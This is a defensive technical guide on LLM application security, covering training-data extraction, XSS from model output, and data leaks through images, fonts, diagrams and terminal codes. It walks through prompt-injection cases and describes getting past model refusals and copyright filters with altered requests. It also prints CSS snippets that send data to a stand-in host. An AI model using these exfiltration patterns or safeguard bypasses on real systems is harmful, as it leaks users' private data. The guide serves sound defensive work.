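In *Extracting Training Data from Large Language Models*, Carlini, Tramèr and colleagues (2020) showed that it was practical to extract memorised training data from GPT-2, an early OpenAI model. They generated 600,000 samples and ranked them by how likely each was to be memorised. The most successful ranking compared GPT-2's confidence in a text with how well an ordinary compression program could shrink it. Repetitive text is predictable to GPT-2 and also compresses well, but if a text is very predictable to GPT-2 and compresses poorly, it was probably in the training data.

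The team picked 1,800 candidates, searched for them on the web and had OpenAI check them against the training data. They confirmed 604 as memorised. Of these, 46 named individuals outside news stories and 32 contained contact details, half of them for private individuals.

They also measured the effect of repetition, using a training document that listed links to Reddit, a discussion site, and repeated some of them many times. The largest version of GPT-2 reproduced every link they tested that appeared at least 33 times, and none that appeared 17 times or fewer. The smallest version reproduced none of the tested links. OpenAI had removed duplicate documents before training, but this did not remove repetition within a document.

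In 2023, Nasr and colleagues spent $200 to extract more than 10,000 distinct passages of training text from ChatGPT, the longest over 4,000 characters. ChatGPT had seemed much safer when they used ordinary extraction prompts, because only 0.02% of the tokens it produced belonged to passages they could match in nine terabytes of web text. A repetitive request made it stop behaving like a chatbot and produce training text about 150 times as often. When they checked 15,000 outputs for personal information, 16.9% contained some that the model had memorised.

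Even these counts were too low. In a sample of 494 outputs, checking against the nine-terabyte collection identified 70 as memorised, while manual web searches identified 150.

The attack worked only on that ChatGPT model, and the team gave OpenAI 90 days' notice before publishing. They also ran the usual memorisation test on the 1,000 longest passages they had extracted, giving ChatGPT all but the last 50 tokens of each. It completed only 3.5% of them exactly, although it had produced all of them before. A chatbot that passes this test may therefore still have memorised a lot, which matters more to anyone auditing a model today than the attack itself.

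*Scalable Extraction of Training Data from Aligned, Production Language Models* (Nasr, Rando and colleagues, 2025) later described two attacks that undo alignment, the training that makes a model act as a helpful assistant. The attacks recovered thousands of training examples. One used OpenAI's public service to fine-tune ChatGPT, which means training it further on new examples. Cooper, a co-author, says this extracted parts of *New York Times* articles.

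### Long passages of books

Ahmed, Cooper and colleagues tried to extract 13 books from four commercial models in August and September 2025 (*Extracting books from production language models*, 2026). They gave each model the opening words of a book and asked it to continue. If that worked, they kept asking for more without supplying any further text from the book. Claude 3.7 Sonnet and GPT-4.1 refused at first, so the team automatically submitted randomly altered versions of the request until one succeeded.

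They counted only near-verbatim passages of at least 100 words, in the book's order. If *m* is the number of words in those passages and |B| is the length of the book, the share recovered is m / |B|. These were the results for the first Harry Potter novel:

| Model | Altered requests before one worked | Share recovered | Longest passage (words) | Cost of the continuation requests |
|---|---|---|---|---|
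| Claude 3.7 Sonnet | 258 | 95.8% | 6,658 | $119.97 |
| GPT-4.1 | 5,179 | 4.0% | 821 | $1.37 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | none needed | 76.8% | 9,070 | $2.44 |
| Grok 3 | none needed | 70.3% | 6,337 | $8.16 |

The table doesn't rank the models by safety, because the team used different settings for each one. Harry Potter was unusually easy to extract, and most attempts on other books still in copyright recovered 10% or less. As a control, the team tried a novel published after the models' training had ended, and none of the four models could continue its opening.

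The safeguards mostly slowed the researchers down without stopping them. Gemini's filter against reciting copyrighted text returned empty answers until the team changed its settings and the wording of its requests. Claude stopped refusing when they asked for shorter replies. GPT-4.1 was the most resistant and always refused at some point in the first chapter, but it sometimes accepted the same request later. When the team published after a 90-day notice period, the method still worked on some of the systems.

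In *Alignment Whack-a-Mole*, Liu, Mireshghallah and colleagues (2026) fine-tuned GPT-4o, Gemini 2.5 Pro and DeepSeek-V3.1 to expand plot summaries into full prose, then gave them summaries of books that were not in the fine-tuning data. They reported that the models reproduced up to 85–90% of some books, including single passages of more than 460 words. Fine-tuning only on Haruki Murakami's novels led the models to reproduce text by more than 30 other authors.

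Cooper accepts the long passages as real extraction but rejects the headline percentage. That percentage includes any match of five words or more, pooled from 100 attempts at every excerpt. The summaries also supplied names, events and phrases that a capable model could reassemble into matching text. When Liu's team fine-tuned GPT-4o on synthetic stories instead, the model still scored 19.4% on *The Handmaid's Tale*, which the team described as close to zero.

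A later version of Liu's paper adds the breakdown by length that Cooper found missing, and the breakdown largely supports Cooper's criticism. In the tests across authors, matches of five to nine words made up 76.6% of the text counted as reproduced, and passages of 50 words or more made up 5.6%. Average coverage was 48.5%, so the long passages amounted to roughly 3% of a book. Some books were exceptions, with much higher shares. Passages of 50 words or more from GPT-4o covered 68.9% of Neil Gaiman's *Coraline*.

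Liu and colleagues also compared two versions of Llama 3.1 405B, an open model from Meta. The version without assistant training readily reproduced text from books, while the version with it almost never did. Fine-tuning the assistant-trained version on Murakami's writing brought most of the text back, so assistant training had suppressed the memorised text without removing it.

These rates apply to models from 2024 and 2025, and newer models may differ. A model that refuses to recite a text may still have memorised it. Famous books probably appear in training data many times, so they are a poor guide to how often private records leak. However, GPT-2 memorised some strings that appeared in only one document.

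### Keeping training data from coming out

A developer who uses a vendor's model can't change what it has already memorised, but can decide what to add. If the support company fine-tunes a model on old tickets, A's phone number may end up in the weights, where no permission check can protect it. It is safer to leave the tickets in a database and retrieve them only for people allowed to see them. If the company needs to fine-tune, it should remove personal details first and let only people who could read the original tickets use the resulting model.

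Deduplication should remove repeated passages within documents as well as whole duplicate documents. It lowers the risk for text that would otherwise appear many times, but it doesn't make a model safe. Nasr and colleagues compared two versions of Pythia, an open model with 6.9 billion parameters. Memorised passages made up 0.596% of the output from the version trained on deduplicated data and 0.548% of the output from the version trained without deduplication.

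Differential privacy is a training method that mathematically guarantees a limit on how much any one record can influence the model. Carlini and colleagues warn that it can lengthen training and usually makes the model less useful. The guarantee depends on what counts as a record. If each ticket counts as one record and A's phone number appears in forty tickets, the guarantee for A's number is much weaker than the guarantee for a single ticket.

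Filters for verbatim text compare an answer with a list of protected passages. They can catch long copies, but they miss anything that isn't on the list and may miss altered copies. A filter that checks each reply separately can also miss a passage that the user collects in small pieces, so it should check the whole conversation.

Rate limits are most useful against bulk extraction. Recovering the Harry Potter novel took 480 continuation requests with Claude and 171 with Gemini. At a limit of 100 requests a day, one account would have needed five days with Claude and two with Gemini. The 5,179 altered requests that GPT-4.1 needed would have taken about 52 days. Rate limits are less useful against someone looking for one phone number, who may need only one successful answer.

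Sanitising HTML doesn't stop an attacker from extracting memorised training data, because a phone number or a page of a novel contains no script or dangerous markup to remove. The attacker reads the text on their own screen, so the browser doesn't have to run anything or contact another server.

Closing outlets helps protect training data only when outsiders can't query the model themselves. If a company fine-tunes a model for its staff alone, an attacker without access could plant a prompt injection that makes the model output memorised text in an employee's session and send it out. The company would then need the same outlet controls that protect its runtime data.

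## Keeping model output from running as script

Whatever a model writes, a developer can keep it from running as script, because the application's own code puts the answer on the page.

### Reflected, stored and DOM-based XSS

Web security divides XSS into three types, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian apply them to applications in which a model stands between the attacker and the page:

- In reflected XSS, the attacker's prompt makes the model produce script, and the chat window displays the answer straight away.
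- In stored XSS, the application saves the answer, perhaps as a ticket, a comment or part of a chat history, and the script runs when somebody opens it later.
- In DOM-based XSS, JavaScript already running on the page inserts the answer unsafely into the DOM, the browser's working copy of the page.

In every type the flaw is in the code that displays the answer as live HTML.

The types can overlap. AnythingLLM, an application for asking questions about documents, had a flaw that was both stored and DOM-based, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-41318* (2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws. An attacker could hide instructions in a shared document that led the model to write a chart caption containing HTML. The caption stayed in the chat history, and its script could run in the browser of every other user who opened the conversation. Version 1.12.1 fixed the flaw.

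Misclassifying a flaw can make it look less serious than it is. In July 2026 the security firm Positive Security reported XSS in its own bank's chatbot, and the bank at first classed it as a reflected flaw that users could only exploit against themselves. *Banking AI XSS* (2026) describes two ways for a stranger to deliver the script. One was an invoice containing white-on-white text, which the victim uploaded so that the chatbot could add the payee. The other was a pair of one-cent payments with instructions in their reference fields, which the chatbot read when the customer asked for a list of transactions.

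Payment references can't contain angle brackets, so a script sent in one would probably have failed against an ordinary banking page. The researchers wrote the brackets as abbreviations and had the model convert them back. Their script then fetched the customer's email address from the bank's systems and sent it to an outside server. In the payment demonstration, the researchers repeated some of the instructions in the victim's own prompt because they didn't want to send many test payments through a live bank. The invoice version needed only an ordinary request. The bank fixed the flaw two days after the report.

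### The DeepSeek case

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian classify the DeepSeek flaw as reflected XSS. Embrace The Red's *DeepSeek AI* describes how Rehberger found it in 2024 by asking the chatbot to print a list of standard XSS test strings. The chat page ran one of them instead of showing it. At that point, only Rehberger's own account was at risk.

To reach other people, Rehberger put instructions in a text file that a user might upload for analysis. The file also held a frame, an HTML element that normally displays another page, with script in place of the page's address. Rehberger encoded the frame in Base64, which rewrites data as letters, digits and a few symbols, because obvious script often triggers firewalls and makes models refuse. DeepSeek's model decoded the text and returned only the frame, which the chat page inserted as live HTML.

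The script displayed the user's cookies and a login token from local storage, where websites keep data in the browser. The token alone was enough to take over the session. The demonstration only showed the token on screen, but sending it to a server would have taken little extra code. Rehberger reported the flaw through the app's contact form, and DeepSeek fixed it a day later.

A site can limit this kind of damage by keeping its login token in a cookie marked HttpOnly, which scripts cannot read. Local storage has no such setting. Even with an HttpOnly cookie, an injected script can make requests as the user for as long as the page is open.

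### Plain text and encoding

The simplest defence is to display the answer as plain text:

```
box.textContent = answer;
```

The browser doesn't parse text inserted this way as HTML, so tags and asterisks appear exactly as the model wrote them. This suits titles, notifications and captions, which seldom need formatting. It would have been enough to keep AnythingLLM's chart captions from running as script.

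An application that builds HTML around the model's text has to encode that text, replacing characters that have a special meaning with codes for displaying them. For example, `<` becomes `&lt;`. OWASP recommends encoding for the context, because different characters are dangerous in different places:

| Where the text goes | What can turn it into code | What to do |
|---|---|---|
| Between two tags | `<` | Encode `&` and `<` |
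| In a quoted attribute | The quotation mark that ends it | Encode quotation marks too |
| In a link's address | An address that begins with `javascript:` | Check the scheme, then encode as an attribute |
| In a block of script | A quotation mark or a closing tag | Keep model text out |

AnythingLLM made the second mistake. It copied an image's description into the `alt` attribute without encoding it. Suppose that the description is `Chart" title="Hello`. The result is:

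```
<img src="chart.png" alt="Chart" title="Hello">
```

The quotation mark after "Chart" ended the description, and the rest became a new attribute. A `title` is harmless, but an attacker could instead add an event handler, which is an attribute containing script that the browser runs when something happens, such as an image loading. Encoding the quotation marks as `&quot;` would have kept the whole description inside `alt`.

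Encoding doesn't make a link's address safe, because `javascript:` contains no characters that need encoding. N45HT's *Hacking AI with Markdown* describes a separate DeepSeek flaw in which a Markdown link ran script when the user clicked it. DeepSeek fixed the flaw by sanitising the Markdown.

The application's code must encode the model's output every time. The bank's chatbot returned some tags as live HTML and others as encoded text. Positive Security found that starting with a simple image tag made the tags after it more likely to be returned as live HTML. This suggests that the model influenced the encoding, although the researchers could only guess at the cause. After the fix, the answers always seemed to be encoded.

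### Markdown parsers and sanitisers

Most chat answers need headings, lists and links, which plain text can't provide. The developer should first turn off raw HTML in the Markdown parser, so that the parser creates tags only from Markdown and encodes any the model wrote. In markdown-it, the setting is `html: false`.

This setting doesn't control HTML that the parser's extensions produce. AnythingLLM's unsafe image description came from a custom rule added to markdown-it. In 5ire, a desktop AI assistant, the diagram plug-in's security level was set to "loose", which let HTML tags back in through the diagram labels, according to *CVE-2025-68669* (2025) from INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute. There was no patch when INCIBE published the entry.

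The next defence is therefore a sanitiser that examines the finished HTML. DOMPurify, a widely used open-source sanitiser, parses the HTML with the browser's own parser, removes whatever is not on its allow-lists and returns the rest. Its default lists are broad. They include SVG and MathML, two notations for drawings and formulas, and link schemes such as `ftp` and `sms`. A chat answer needs much less:

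```
const answerRules = {
  ALLOWED_TAGS: ['p', 'strong', 'em', 'ul', 'ol', 'li', 'code', 'pre', 'a'],
  ALLOWED_ATTR: ['href'],
  ALLOW_DATA_ATTR: false,
  ALLOW_ARIA_ATTR: false,
  ALLOWED_URI_REGEXP: /^https?:/i
};
const clean = DOMPurify.sanitize(html, answerRules);
```

These rules permit nine elements and one attribute, and links only to `http` and `https` addresses.

DOMPurify needs a reliable parser. In very old browsers it returns the text unchanged, so the application should check its `isSupported` property first. On a server it relies on a separate package, such as jsdom or happy-dom, to imitate the browser. Its documentation recommends an up-to-date version of jsdom and warns that using happy-dom will probably lead to XSS.

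### Why regular expressions fail

Some developers search the answer for dangerous patterns with regular expressions, which describe sequences of characters, to save effort. These searches can miss code that a browser will still run, because the browser ignores capitalisation in tag names, repairs unfinished tags and decodes character codes inside attributes. One of DOMPurify's test samples contains the word `javascript` with a capital letter in the middle and an encoded tab character splitting it. A search for "javascript:" would miss it, but the browser removes the tab and reads the word whole.

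Deleting a match can also create the string the filter was looking for. If a filter removes `<script>` once from `<scr<script>ipt>`, the remaining pieces join to form `<script>`.

Another weakness of lists of forbidden items is that the developer has to know every dangerous item in advance. Some filter at the bank blocked the best-known event handler for images but let through an obscure one, and the researchers had their first script running within two minutes of opening the chatbot. An allow-list would have blocked both handlers, because it would include neither.

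The rules above do contain one regular expression, for link addresses. It is safe there because DOMPurify applies it to a single address that the parser has already separated and decoded.

### One answer through two pipelines

Suppose that a model writes this answer, in which a harmless script changes the title of the browser tab:

```
**Saved.** See [the guide](https://example.com/guide). <img src="/logo.png" onload="document.title='Changed'">
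```

In an unsafe pipeline, the parser accepts raw HTML and produces:

```
<p><strong>Saved.</strong> See <a href="https://example.com/guide">the guide</a>. <img src="/logo.png" onload="document.title='Changed'"></p>
```

The page then runs `box.innerHTML = html`. The browser loads the logo and runs the handler, which changes the title, even though the answer contains no script tag.

In a safe pipeline, the parser has raw HTML turned off:

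```
<p><strong>Saved.</strong> See <a href="https://example.com/guide">the guide</a>. &lt;img src=&quot;/logo.png&quot; onload=&quot;document.title='Changed'&quot;&gt;</p>
```

The sanitiser finds nothing to remove. It writes the quotation marks normally again, because they have no special meaning between tags:

```
<p><strong>Saved.</strong> See <a href="https://example.com/guide">the guide</a>. &lt;img src="/logo.png" onload="document.title='Changed'"&gt;</p>
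```

The user sees bold text, a working link and an image tag spelled out in letters. The title doesn't change.

If a colleague later turns raw HTML back on, the sanitiser receives the live image and deletes it, since `img` is not on the allow-list:

```
<p><strong>Saved.</strong> See <a href="https://example.com/guide">the guide</a>. </p>
```

DOMPurify's default rules would have removed only the handler and kept `<img src="/logo.png">`.

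### Changing the HTML after sanitising

DOMPurify's documentation warns that modifying HTML after sanitising it can easily undo the protection. For example, a developer might respond to complaints about stray `&lt;` codes in code samples by adding a line after the sanitiser that turns `&lt;` and `&gt;` back into angle brackets. The samples then look right, but the image tag in the example is live again and its script runs. Search highlighting, emoji replacement and automatic linking can cause similar trouble if they edit the HTML as a string, so they should run before the sanitiser.

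Even an application that changes nothing can have a subtler version of this problem. Frederik Braun explains in *Why the Sanitizer API is just setHTML()* that the usual code parses the HTML twice. The sanitiser parses it, removes the dangerous parts and converts the result to a string, which the browser parses again when the page inserts it. The HTML can change meaning between the two parses, partly because the parser treats the same text differently depending on the surrounding element, and the sanitiser usually parses without that information. Attackers can therefore write HTML that is harmless in the first parse but contains script in the second, an attack known as mutation XSS.

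Braun helped to specify a browser function that avoids the second parse:

```
box.setHTML(html);
```

With `setHTML()`, the browser parses the text once, in the context of the element that will contain it, then sanitises the result and inserts it directly. The function returns no string that a developer could alter or put in the wrong place. Mozilla's *Goodbye innerHTML, Hello setHTML* announced it for Firefox 148 in February 2026. Chrome and Edge support it from version 146, but web.dev's *Safe DOM manipulation with the Sanitizer API* lists Safari as not supporting it, so many applications still need DOMPurify as well.

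### Making the browser enforce the sanitiser

A sanitiser protects only the output that is passed through it. AnythingLLM's developers used DOMPurify everywhere they displayed Markdown except in the chart captions. Such gaps are hard to find by reading code. W3C's *Trusted Types* (2024) counts more than 60 browser features that can turn text into running script, and gives `foo[bar] = aString` as an example of a line that may or may not use one, depending on the values when it runs.

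Trusted Types lets the browser catch these mistakes. The developer defines a policy, a function through which text must pass before the page can use it as HTML:

```
const answers = trustedTypes.createPolicy("answers", {
  createHTML: html => DOMPurify.sanitize(html, answerRules)
});
box.innerHTML = answers.createHTML(html);
```

Once the page enforces Trusted Types, assigning an ordinary string to `innerHTML` causes an error instead of displaying it. If developers forget to call the sanitiser, they see a broken caption during testing. According to MDN's *Trusted Types API*, the feature has worked in the latest versions of all main browsers since February 2026. For older code, a policy named "default" can sanitise strings automatically while developers find and replace the unsafe lines.

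The browser checks that text went through a policy, but not that the policy does anything useful. A policy that returns its input unchanged satisfies the rule and gives no protection. Braun argues in *Perfect types with `setHTML()`* that maintaining policies takes constant attention from people who understand security, and suggests allowing no policies at all. The older functions then reject all strings, so developers have to use `setHTML()`. This design is cleaner, but an application that adopts it needs another way to show formatted answers in Safari until that browser supports `setHTML()`.

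### Forbidding inline script

The last defence on a web page is a Content Security Policy that stops script from running even if it gets past everything else. A policy for the example page could be:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  script-src 'nonce-R4nd0mValue';
  base-uri 'none';
  require-trusted-types-for 'script';
  trusted-types answers dompurify
```

The nonce is a random value that the server must generate anew each time it sends the page. The server puts the same value on its own script tags, and the browser runs only those scripts. An attacker whose text reached the model earlier can't know the value. Event handlers and `javascript:` links can't carry a nonce, so the browser blocks them. The `base-uri` rule stops injected HTML from redirecting the page's own scripts to another server. The last two lines enforce Trusted Types and name the permitted policies. DOMPurify needs its own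 entry because it also has to parse HTML.

With this policy, the title would stay the same even in the unsafe pipeline. The bank had no Content Security Policy, so the injected handler could load a larger script from the researchers' server. To keep old code working, developers sometimes add `'unsafe-inline'` to a policy without nonces, which allows event handlers again and removes most of the policy's benefit.

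A script rule doesn't stop the browser from displaying injected HTML. An attacker could still put a false message or a fake login form in the answer, so the policy can't replace the sanitiser. Pages meant to run a model's code, such as previews of generated websites, can't use these script rules and need isolation instead.

### Desktop applications

Many desktop AI assistants are web pages inside a program. They often use Electron, a framework that combines a browser with Node.js, which lets JavaScript open files and start other programs. If the page has access to Node.js, an attacker can use XSS to take over the computer.

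AnythingLLM's desktop version had this flaw. The US National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2026-32626 Detail* traces it to the same unencoded image description. The program sanitised saved messages but not answers that were still arriving, so partial answers need sanitising too. The victim only had to ask a question in a workspace that contained a hostile document. Wiz's *CVE-2026-32626* attributes the flaw's severity to two Electron settings. `nodeIntegration` was on, which gave the page access to Node.js, and `contextIsolation`, which separates the page's script from the program's more powerful code, was off.

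Version 1.11.2 fixed the flaw in March 2026 by sanitising answers as they arrived. The developers did not change the image rule, and the chart-caption flaw, which became known in April, used the same rule. Encoding the description at its source would have fixed both flaws.

Even with correct Electron settings, injected script can still call the functions that the program deliberately offers to the page. In 5ire, these included one for adding tool servers. According to ReleaseAlert's *CVE-2026-22792*, an injected image handler could call that function to run commands on the computer. Version 0.15.3 fixed the flaw. A safer design would offer the page only narrow functions, and would start a program only after the user confirms it in a dialog that the page's scripts can't click.

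Links also need stricter rules in desktop applications, which may pass an address to the operating system, where some URL schemes start other software. DeepChat, an open-source AI agent application, restricted the function that opened links but left links that open pop-up windows unrestricted. A Markdown link could therefore still lead to code running on the computer, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-43899* (2026). Version 1.0.4-beta.1 included a second fix.

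### Terminals

Coding assistants often print their answers in a terminal, a text window for typing commands. Terminals don't run JavaScript, but they act on control codes mixed in with the text. These codes, most of which begin with the escape character (ASCII 27), can change colours, move the cursor or clear the screen. Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* showed in 2024 that models can produce such codes and that a web page could make a summarising tool print them. Depending on the terminal, the codes could hide text, write to the clipboard or, in Apple's Terminal, leak data through a network lookup without the user clicking anything.

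GitHub's command-line tool had this flaw until version 2.97.0. It printed text from outsiders, including the content of AI agents' tasks, without neutralising control codes. OSV's *CVE-2026-64654* (2026) lists possible effects ranging from a changed window title to, in some terminals, running a command. GitHub had already fixed the problem in one command, and version 2.97.0 extended the fix to the others.

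The terminal itself can also be vulnerable. Warp, a terminal with built-in AI agents, let any printed text read or replace the clipboard without asking the user. *When Terminal Output Owns Your Clipboard* (Pelaseyed, 2026) demonstrated this on the Mac version. Text from a model or a web page could swap a copied command for another before the user pasted it. A May 2026 release added a setting that refuses clipboard access by default.

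Control codes are especially dangerous in approval prompts, where the user relies on the screen to decide what an agent may do. In OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent, a tool's title could contain codes that altered the text the user saw in the prompt. The developers fixed this in March 2026. According to OSV's *GHSA-4hmj-39m8-jwc7* (2026), part of the fix was to broaden a pattern that had stripped only some kinds of control code.

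It is safer to make every control character visible than to search for known sequences. Rehberger recommends caret notation, which writes each control character as a caret and a printable one. The printable character's number is 64 higher, so escape (27) becomes `^[`, because 27 + 64 = 91 and character 91 is `[`. A short Python function can do this:

```
def make_visible(text):
    shown = ""
    for ch in text:
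        n = ord(ch)
        if ch in "\n\t":
            shown += ch
        elif n < 32:
            shown += "^" + chr(n + 64)
        elif 127 <= n <= 159:
            shown += f"<{n}>"
        else:
            shown += ch
    return shown
```

The function keeps line breaks and tabs. It also filters characters 127 to 159, because some terminals treat some of them as commands. A program can add its own colour codes afterwards, as long as it never copies them from the model's text.

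## Stopping images, fonts and diagrams from carrying data out

A page can leak data without running any script. Browsers download the images, fonts and stylesheets that a page references, and the addresses of these files can carry private data.

### What a browser loads by itself

A link waits for a click, while an image loads at once. Otsukare's *List of elements/attributes having URL for value in html5* (2011) sorts HTML's attributes on this basis, calling an address passive if it waits and active if it loads with the page. Some of the elements on the list are obsolete now, but the distinction still tells a developer which parts of an answer need attention:

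| Feature | What makes the browser send a request |
|---|---|
| Images | `src` on `img`, or a picture inside an SVG drawing |
| Sound and video | `src` on `audio`, `video`, `source` and `track`, or a video's `poster` |
| Embedded pages and files | `src` on `iframe` and `embed`, or `data` on `object` |
| Image buttons in forms | `src` on `input` |
| Stylesheets | `href` on `link`, and addresses inside the CSS, such as backgrounds and fonts |
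| Diagrams and charts | Pictures in the drawing, or a data file for a chart |

CSS is easy to overlook because its addresses can sit in a block of styling text, where a filter that looks for image tags won't find them. This stylesheet sends out the same note as an image would:

```
@font-face {
  font-family: "Note";
  src: url("https://example.com/font.woff2?note=meeting-at-noon");
}
h1 { font-family: "Note"; }
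```

The browser requests the font when the page has a heading that uses it. The font doesn't have to exist, because the server receives the requested address either way. Hiding an image with CSS usually doesn't help, because most browsers download it anyway.

Many sanitisers, including DOMPurify with its default rules, allow images because an image can't run script. The default rules for the browser's own `setHTML()`, listed in MDN's *Default sanitizer configuration*, are stricter and remove `src` from images, audio and video. But if a developer passes in a custom configuration, the browser guarantees only to remove what could run script, so a developer who writes a new list to permit images also permits whatever addresses the model puts in them. The `answerRules` list for DOMPurify avoids this problem because nothing it permits loads automatically.

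### How much fits in one address

Addresses can't hold every character, so attackers often have the model encode the data in Base64. This encoding writes every three bytes as four characters, so *n* bytes become 4 × ⌈n/3⌉ characters. A 1,200-byte email becomes 4 × 400 = 1,600 characters, which leaves 400 for the server's name and path in a 2,000-character address. Hexadecimal, which uses two characters for each byte, would need 2,400 characters and wouldn't fit.

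The 2,000-character figure is cautious, since current browsers and many servers accept longer addresses. An answer can also contain several images, and ten of them could carry a 12,000-byte document in pieces of 1,200 bytes.

Limiting the length of addresses therefore does little good. It might stop a whole email from leaving, but a six-digit login code needs only six characters. The model's own mistakes may be more of an obstacle, because it has to write out the encoded text itself, but it doesn't always make enough of them to matter. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes how GitLab's coding assistant encoded changes from a private project in Base64 and put them in an image's address, which let the researchers read the code.

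### Choosing a rule for external images

The simplest rule, which Google chose for Gemini, is to show no images from other sites. Tenable, a security company that tested Gemini from outside, also saw it filtering image Markdown and sending links through a google.com address. With this rule, users see a link or a caption instead of product pictures, maps and logos from the web. The application can still use its own server to show charts it has drawn and files the user has uploaded.

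Such a rule protects only the products that apply it. Noma Labs found a way to make Google's Gemini Enterprise put search results into an image's address, using instructions planted in an email, a calendar invitation or a shared document. SC Media reports that the attack, named GeminiJack, began when an employee made a routine search. Google has since addressed it. Google's coding tool Antigravity also displays images in its chat. A researcher quoted by Willison reported this in November 2025, and Google flagged the report as intended behaviour. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (June 2026) used the same feature in an attack that started from instructions in a web page's title.

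A second approach is to load an image only after the user agrees. Continue, an AI extension for the code editor VS Code, adopted this in August 2025, a day after the security firm VerSprite reported a data leak through images. According to VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*, the extension now asks before loading external images and restricts access to certain files. The user has to click for each picture, and the click is a poor safeguard if the prompt shows only a long address, because a Base64 copy of an email looks much like the random identifiers in many legitimate image addresses. Users are more likely to recognise the server's name, so the prompt should display it prominently.

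An application can also load images only from named hosts. GitLab fixed its assistant this way, refusing to display images and forms that point outside gitlab.com. Users see the images they need most, as long as someone keeps the list of hosts up to date. But data can still go to any host on the list, so someone also has to audit the list.

A looser variant loads any address that a search engine has already indexed as public. An address the model has just made up from a stolen email won't be in the index. Embrace The Red reports that Google and OpenAI both use this idea, and its *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* explains that small leaks remain possible because the choice between several public addresses can itself convey information. Suppose an attacker gets 60 pictures indexed, one for each digit in each position of a six-digit code. The six that the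 browser requests then reveal the code. Rehberger suggests refusing to load the same address twice in a session. That would stop an attacker from using ten pictures for all six positions, but not from using 60.

| Rule | What the user loses | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| No external images | Pictures from other sites | Fonts, stylesheets or diagrams still load |
| Load after a click | A click for each picture | The user approves an address without understanding it |
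| Named hosts only | Pictures from all other hosts | A named host passes data to an attacker |
| Known public addresses only | New and private pictures | Small amounts leak through the choice of address |

The first rule is usually the right one for an assistant that reads private mail or customer records, because it doesn't depend on the user's judgement or on a list that someone has to maintain.

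Makers of coding tools have been slow to learn this, although their assistants can often read any file in a project. Continue's chat pane displayed Markdown images from any server, so a comment hidden in a source file could make the assistant read the `.env` file, where developers keep passwords and access keys, and send its contents out in an image's address. Sourcegraph fixed the same flaw in Amp soon after Rehberger reported it in June 2025, according to Embrace The Red's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Amp Code*. Rehberger had reported the flaw in Cline in May 2025, and it was still unfixed when he published it more than 90 days later, according to Embrace The Red's *Cline*. Cline's users could reduce the damage by requiring approval for each file the assistant reads, but this did not protect secrets already in the conversation.

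### The gap in Copilot's HTML preview

In autumn 2025 Microsoft 365 Copilot gained a feature that displayed HTML inside the chat. It removed `img` tags, and when Rehberger asked for a page with a heading and an external image, only the heading appeared. Rehberger then asked Copilot to write a page using as many methods as it could for loading an outside resource. One of them, a background image set in CSS, worked.

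The page's Content Security Policy blocked many background images, but its list of permitted servers was long and differed between Word, Excel and the other places where Copilot runs. The rules for fonts were looser, and a font URL in the stylesheet triggered a request to Rehberger's test server from both Word and Excel. Embrace The Red calls the font method the more universal of the two bypasses.

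The attack still needed the user to switch to the preview, because Copilot showed the HTML as code by default and the browser fetched nothing in that view. Rehberger added a request to the injected instructions asking Copilot to show the preview, and Copilot opened it without a click. A safeguard that depends on the user choosing a view works only if the model cannot change the view.

Rehberger reported the CSS and font leaks on October 16, 2025. Microsoft reproduced them in November and completed the fix on March 5, 2026, 140 days after the report. The flaw is CVE-2026-24299.

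Adding `style` to the list of forbidden tags would have blocked both routes Rehberger used, but not a route through the `style` attribute or a video's poster. An allow-list like `answerRules` would have excluded all of these. If a preview has to show styled pages, filtering alone is a weak defence, so the browser also needs a rule that blocks outside requests whatever the HTML contains.

### Diagrams

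Many assistants can draw diagrams with Mermaid, a library that turns a text description into a drawing. A chat page may block images in Markdown but still let Mermaid load them, because Mermaid creates the drawing with its own code.

*Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examined eight coding agents and found this fault in one, which it did not name. A label in a Mermaid diagram could contain an image tag, and Mermaid also has a shape that displays a picture from an address. The team put instructions in an issue on a code-hosting site. When the user asked the agent to fetch the project's issues, the agent read a configuration file from the user's home directory, copied an access key from it into a diagram and drew the diagram, which leaked the key. The agent needed no approval to read files outside the project or to draw a diagram. Someone else had already reported the leak when the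 team did.

Cursor, an AI code editor, had a leak of this kind too (CVE-2025-54132). Rehberger demonstrated it by hiding instructions in a comment in a small C program. When asked to explain the program, Cursor drew a diagram that sent out its saved memories about the developer. A second version of the demonstration sent out access keys. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* points out that a user can sometimes watch a long image address appear in an ordinary chat answer, but the diagram appeared without showing one first. Cursor released an incomplete fix in version 1.3 in July 2025, and CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589* records further bypasses in versions up to 1.6.

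In another case from 2025, Copilot drew a diagram containing a fake "Login" button. Clicking it opened a link that sent stolen emails, encoded in hexadecimal, to the attacker's server. Microsoft responded by disabling links in Copilot's diagrams, according to CyberMaterial.

Mermaid has four security levels, which Snyk's *More than flowcharts* (2026) sets out:

| Level | HTML in labels | Clickable parts |
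|---|---|---|
| `strict` (default) | Shown as text | Off |
| `antiscript` | Allowed, except script elements | On |
| `loose` | Allowed | On |
| `sandbox` | Drawn inside a sandboxed frame | May not work |

Developers sometimes lower the level to restore a feature. Dify, a platform for building AI applications, had used `sandbox`, which interfered with its colour themes. Its developers switched to `loose` and added a filter to block script in links, but the filter covered only flowcharts, so a link in a Gantt chart could still run script. Version 1.11.2 changed the level to `strict`.

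Mermaid's `strict` level stops an image tag in a label from becoming an image. It may not block images added through Mermaid's picture shape, because that shape isn't HTML. Snyk advises passing the finished drawing through a sanitiser, which helps against scripts but can be too late for images. Mermaid builds the drawing in the live page to measure its parts, so the browser may request a picture before the sanitiser runs. The page that draws the diagram therefore needs a browser rule limiting where images may come from.

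Mermaid has also let diagrams add CSS to the page around them, through three flaws disclosed in 2026. The text of a diagram can include settings, such as the font for its labels, and OSV's *GHSA-87f9-hvmw-gh4p* (2026) explains that a specially written setting could end the diagram's own styles and start rules that applied to the whole page. Injected rules could define fonts and also examine attributes elsewhere on the page. A rule of this form would do it:

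```
body:has(input[value^="7"]) {
  background-image: url("https://example.com/starts-with-7");
}
```

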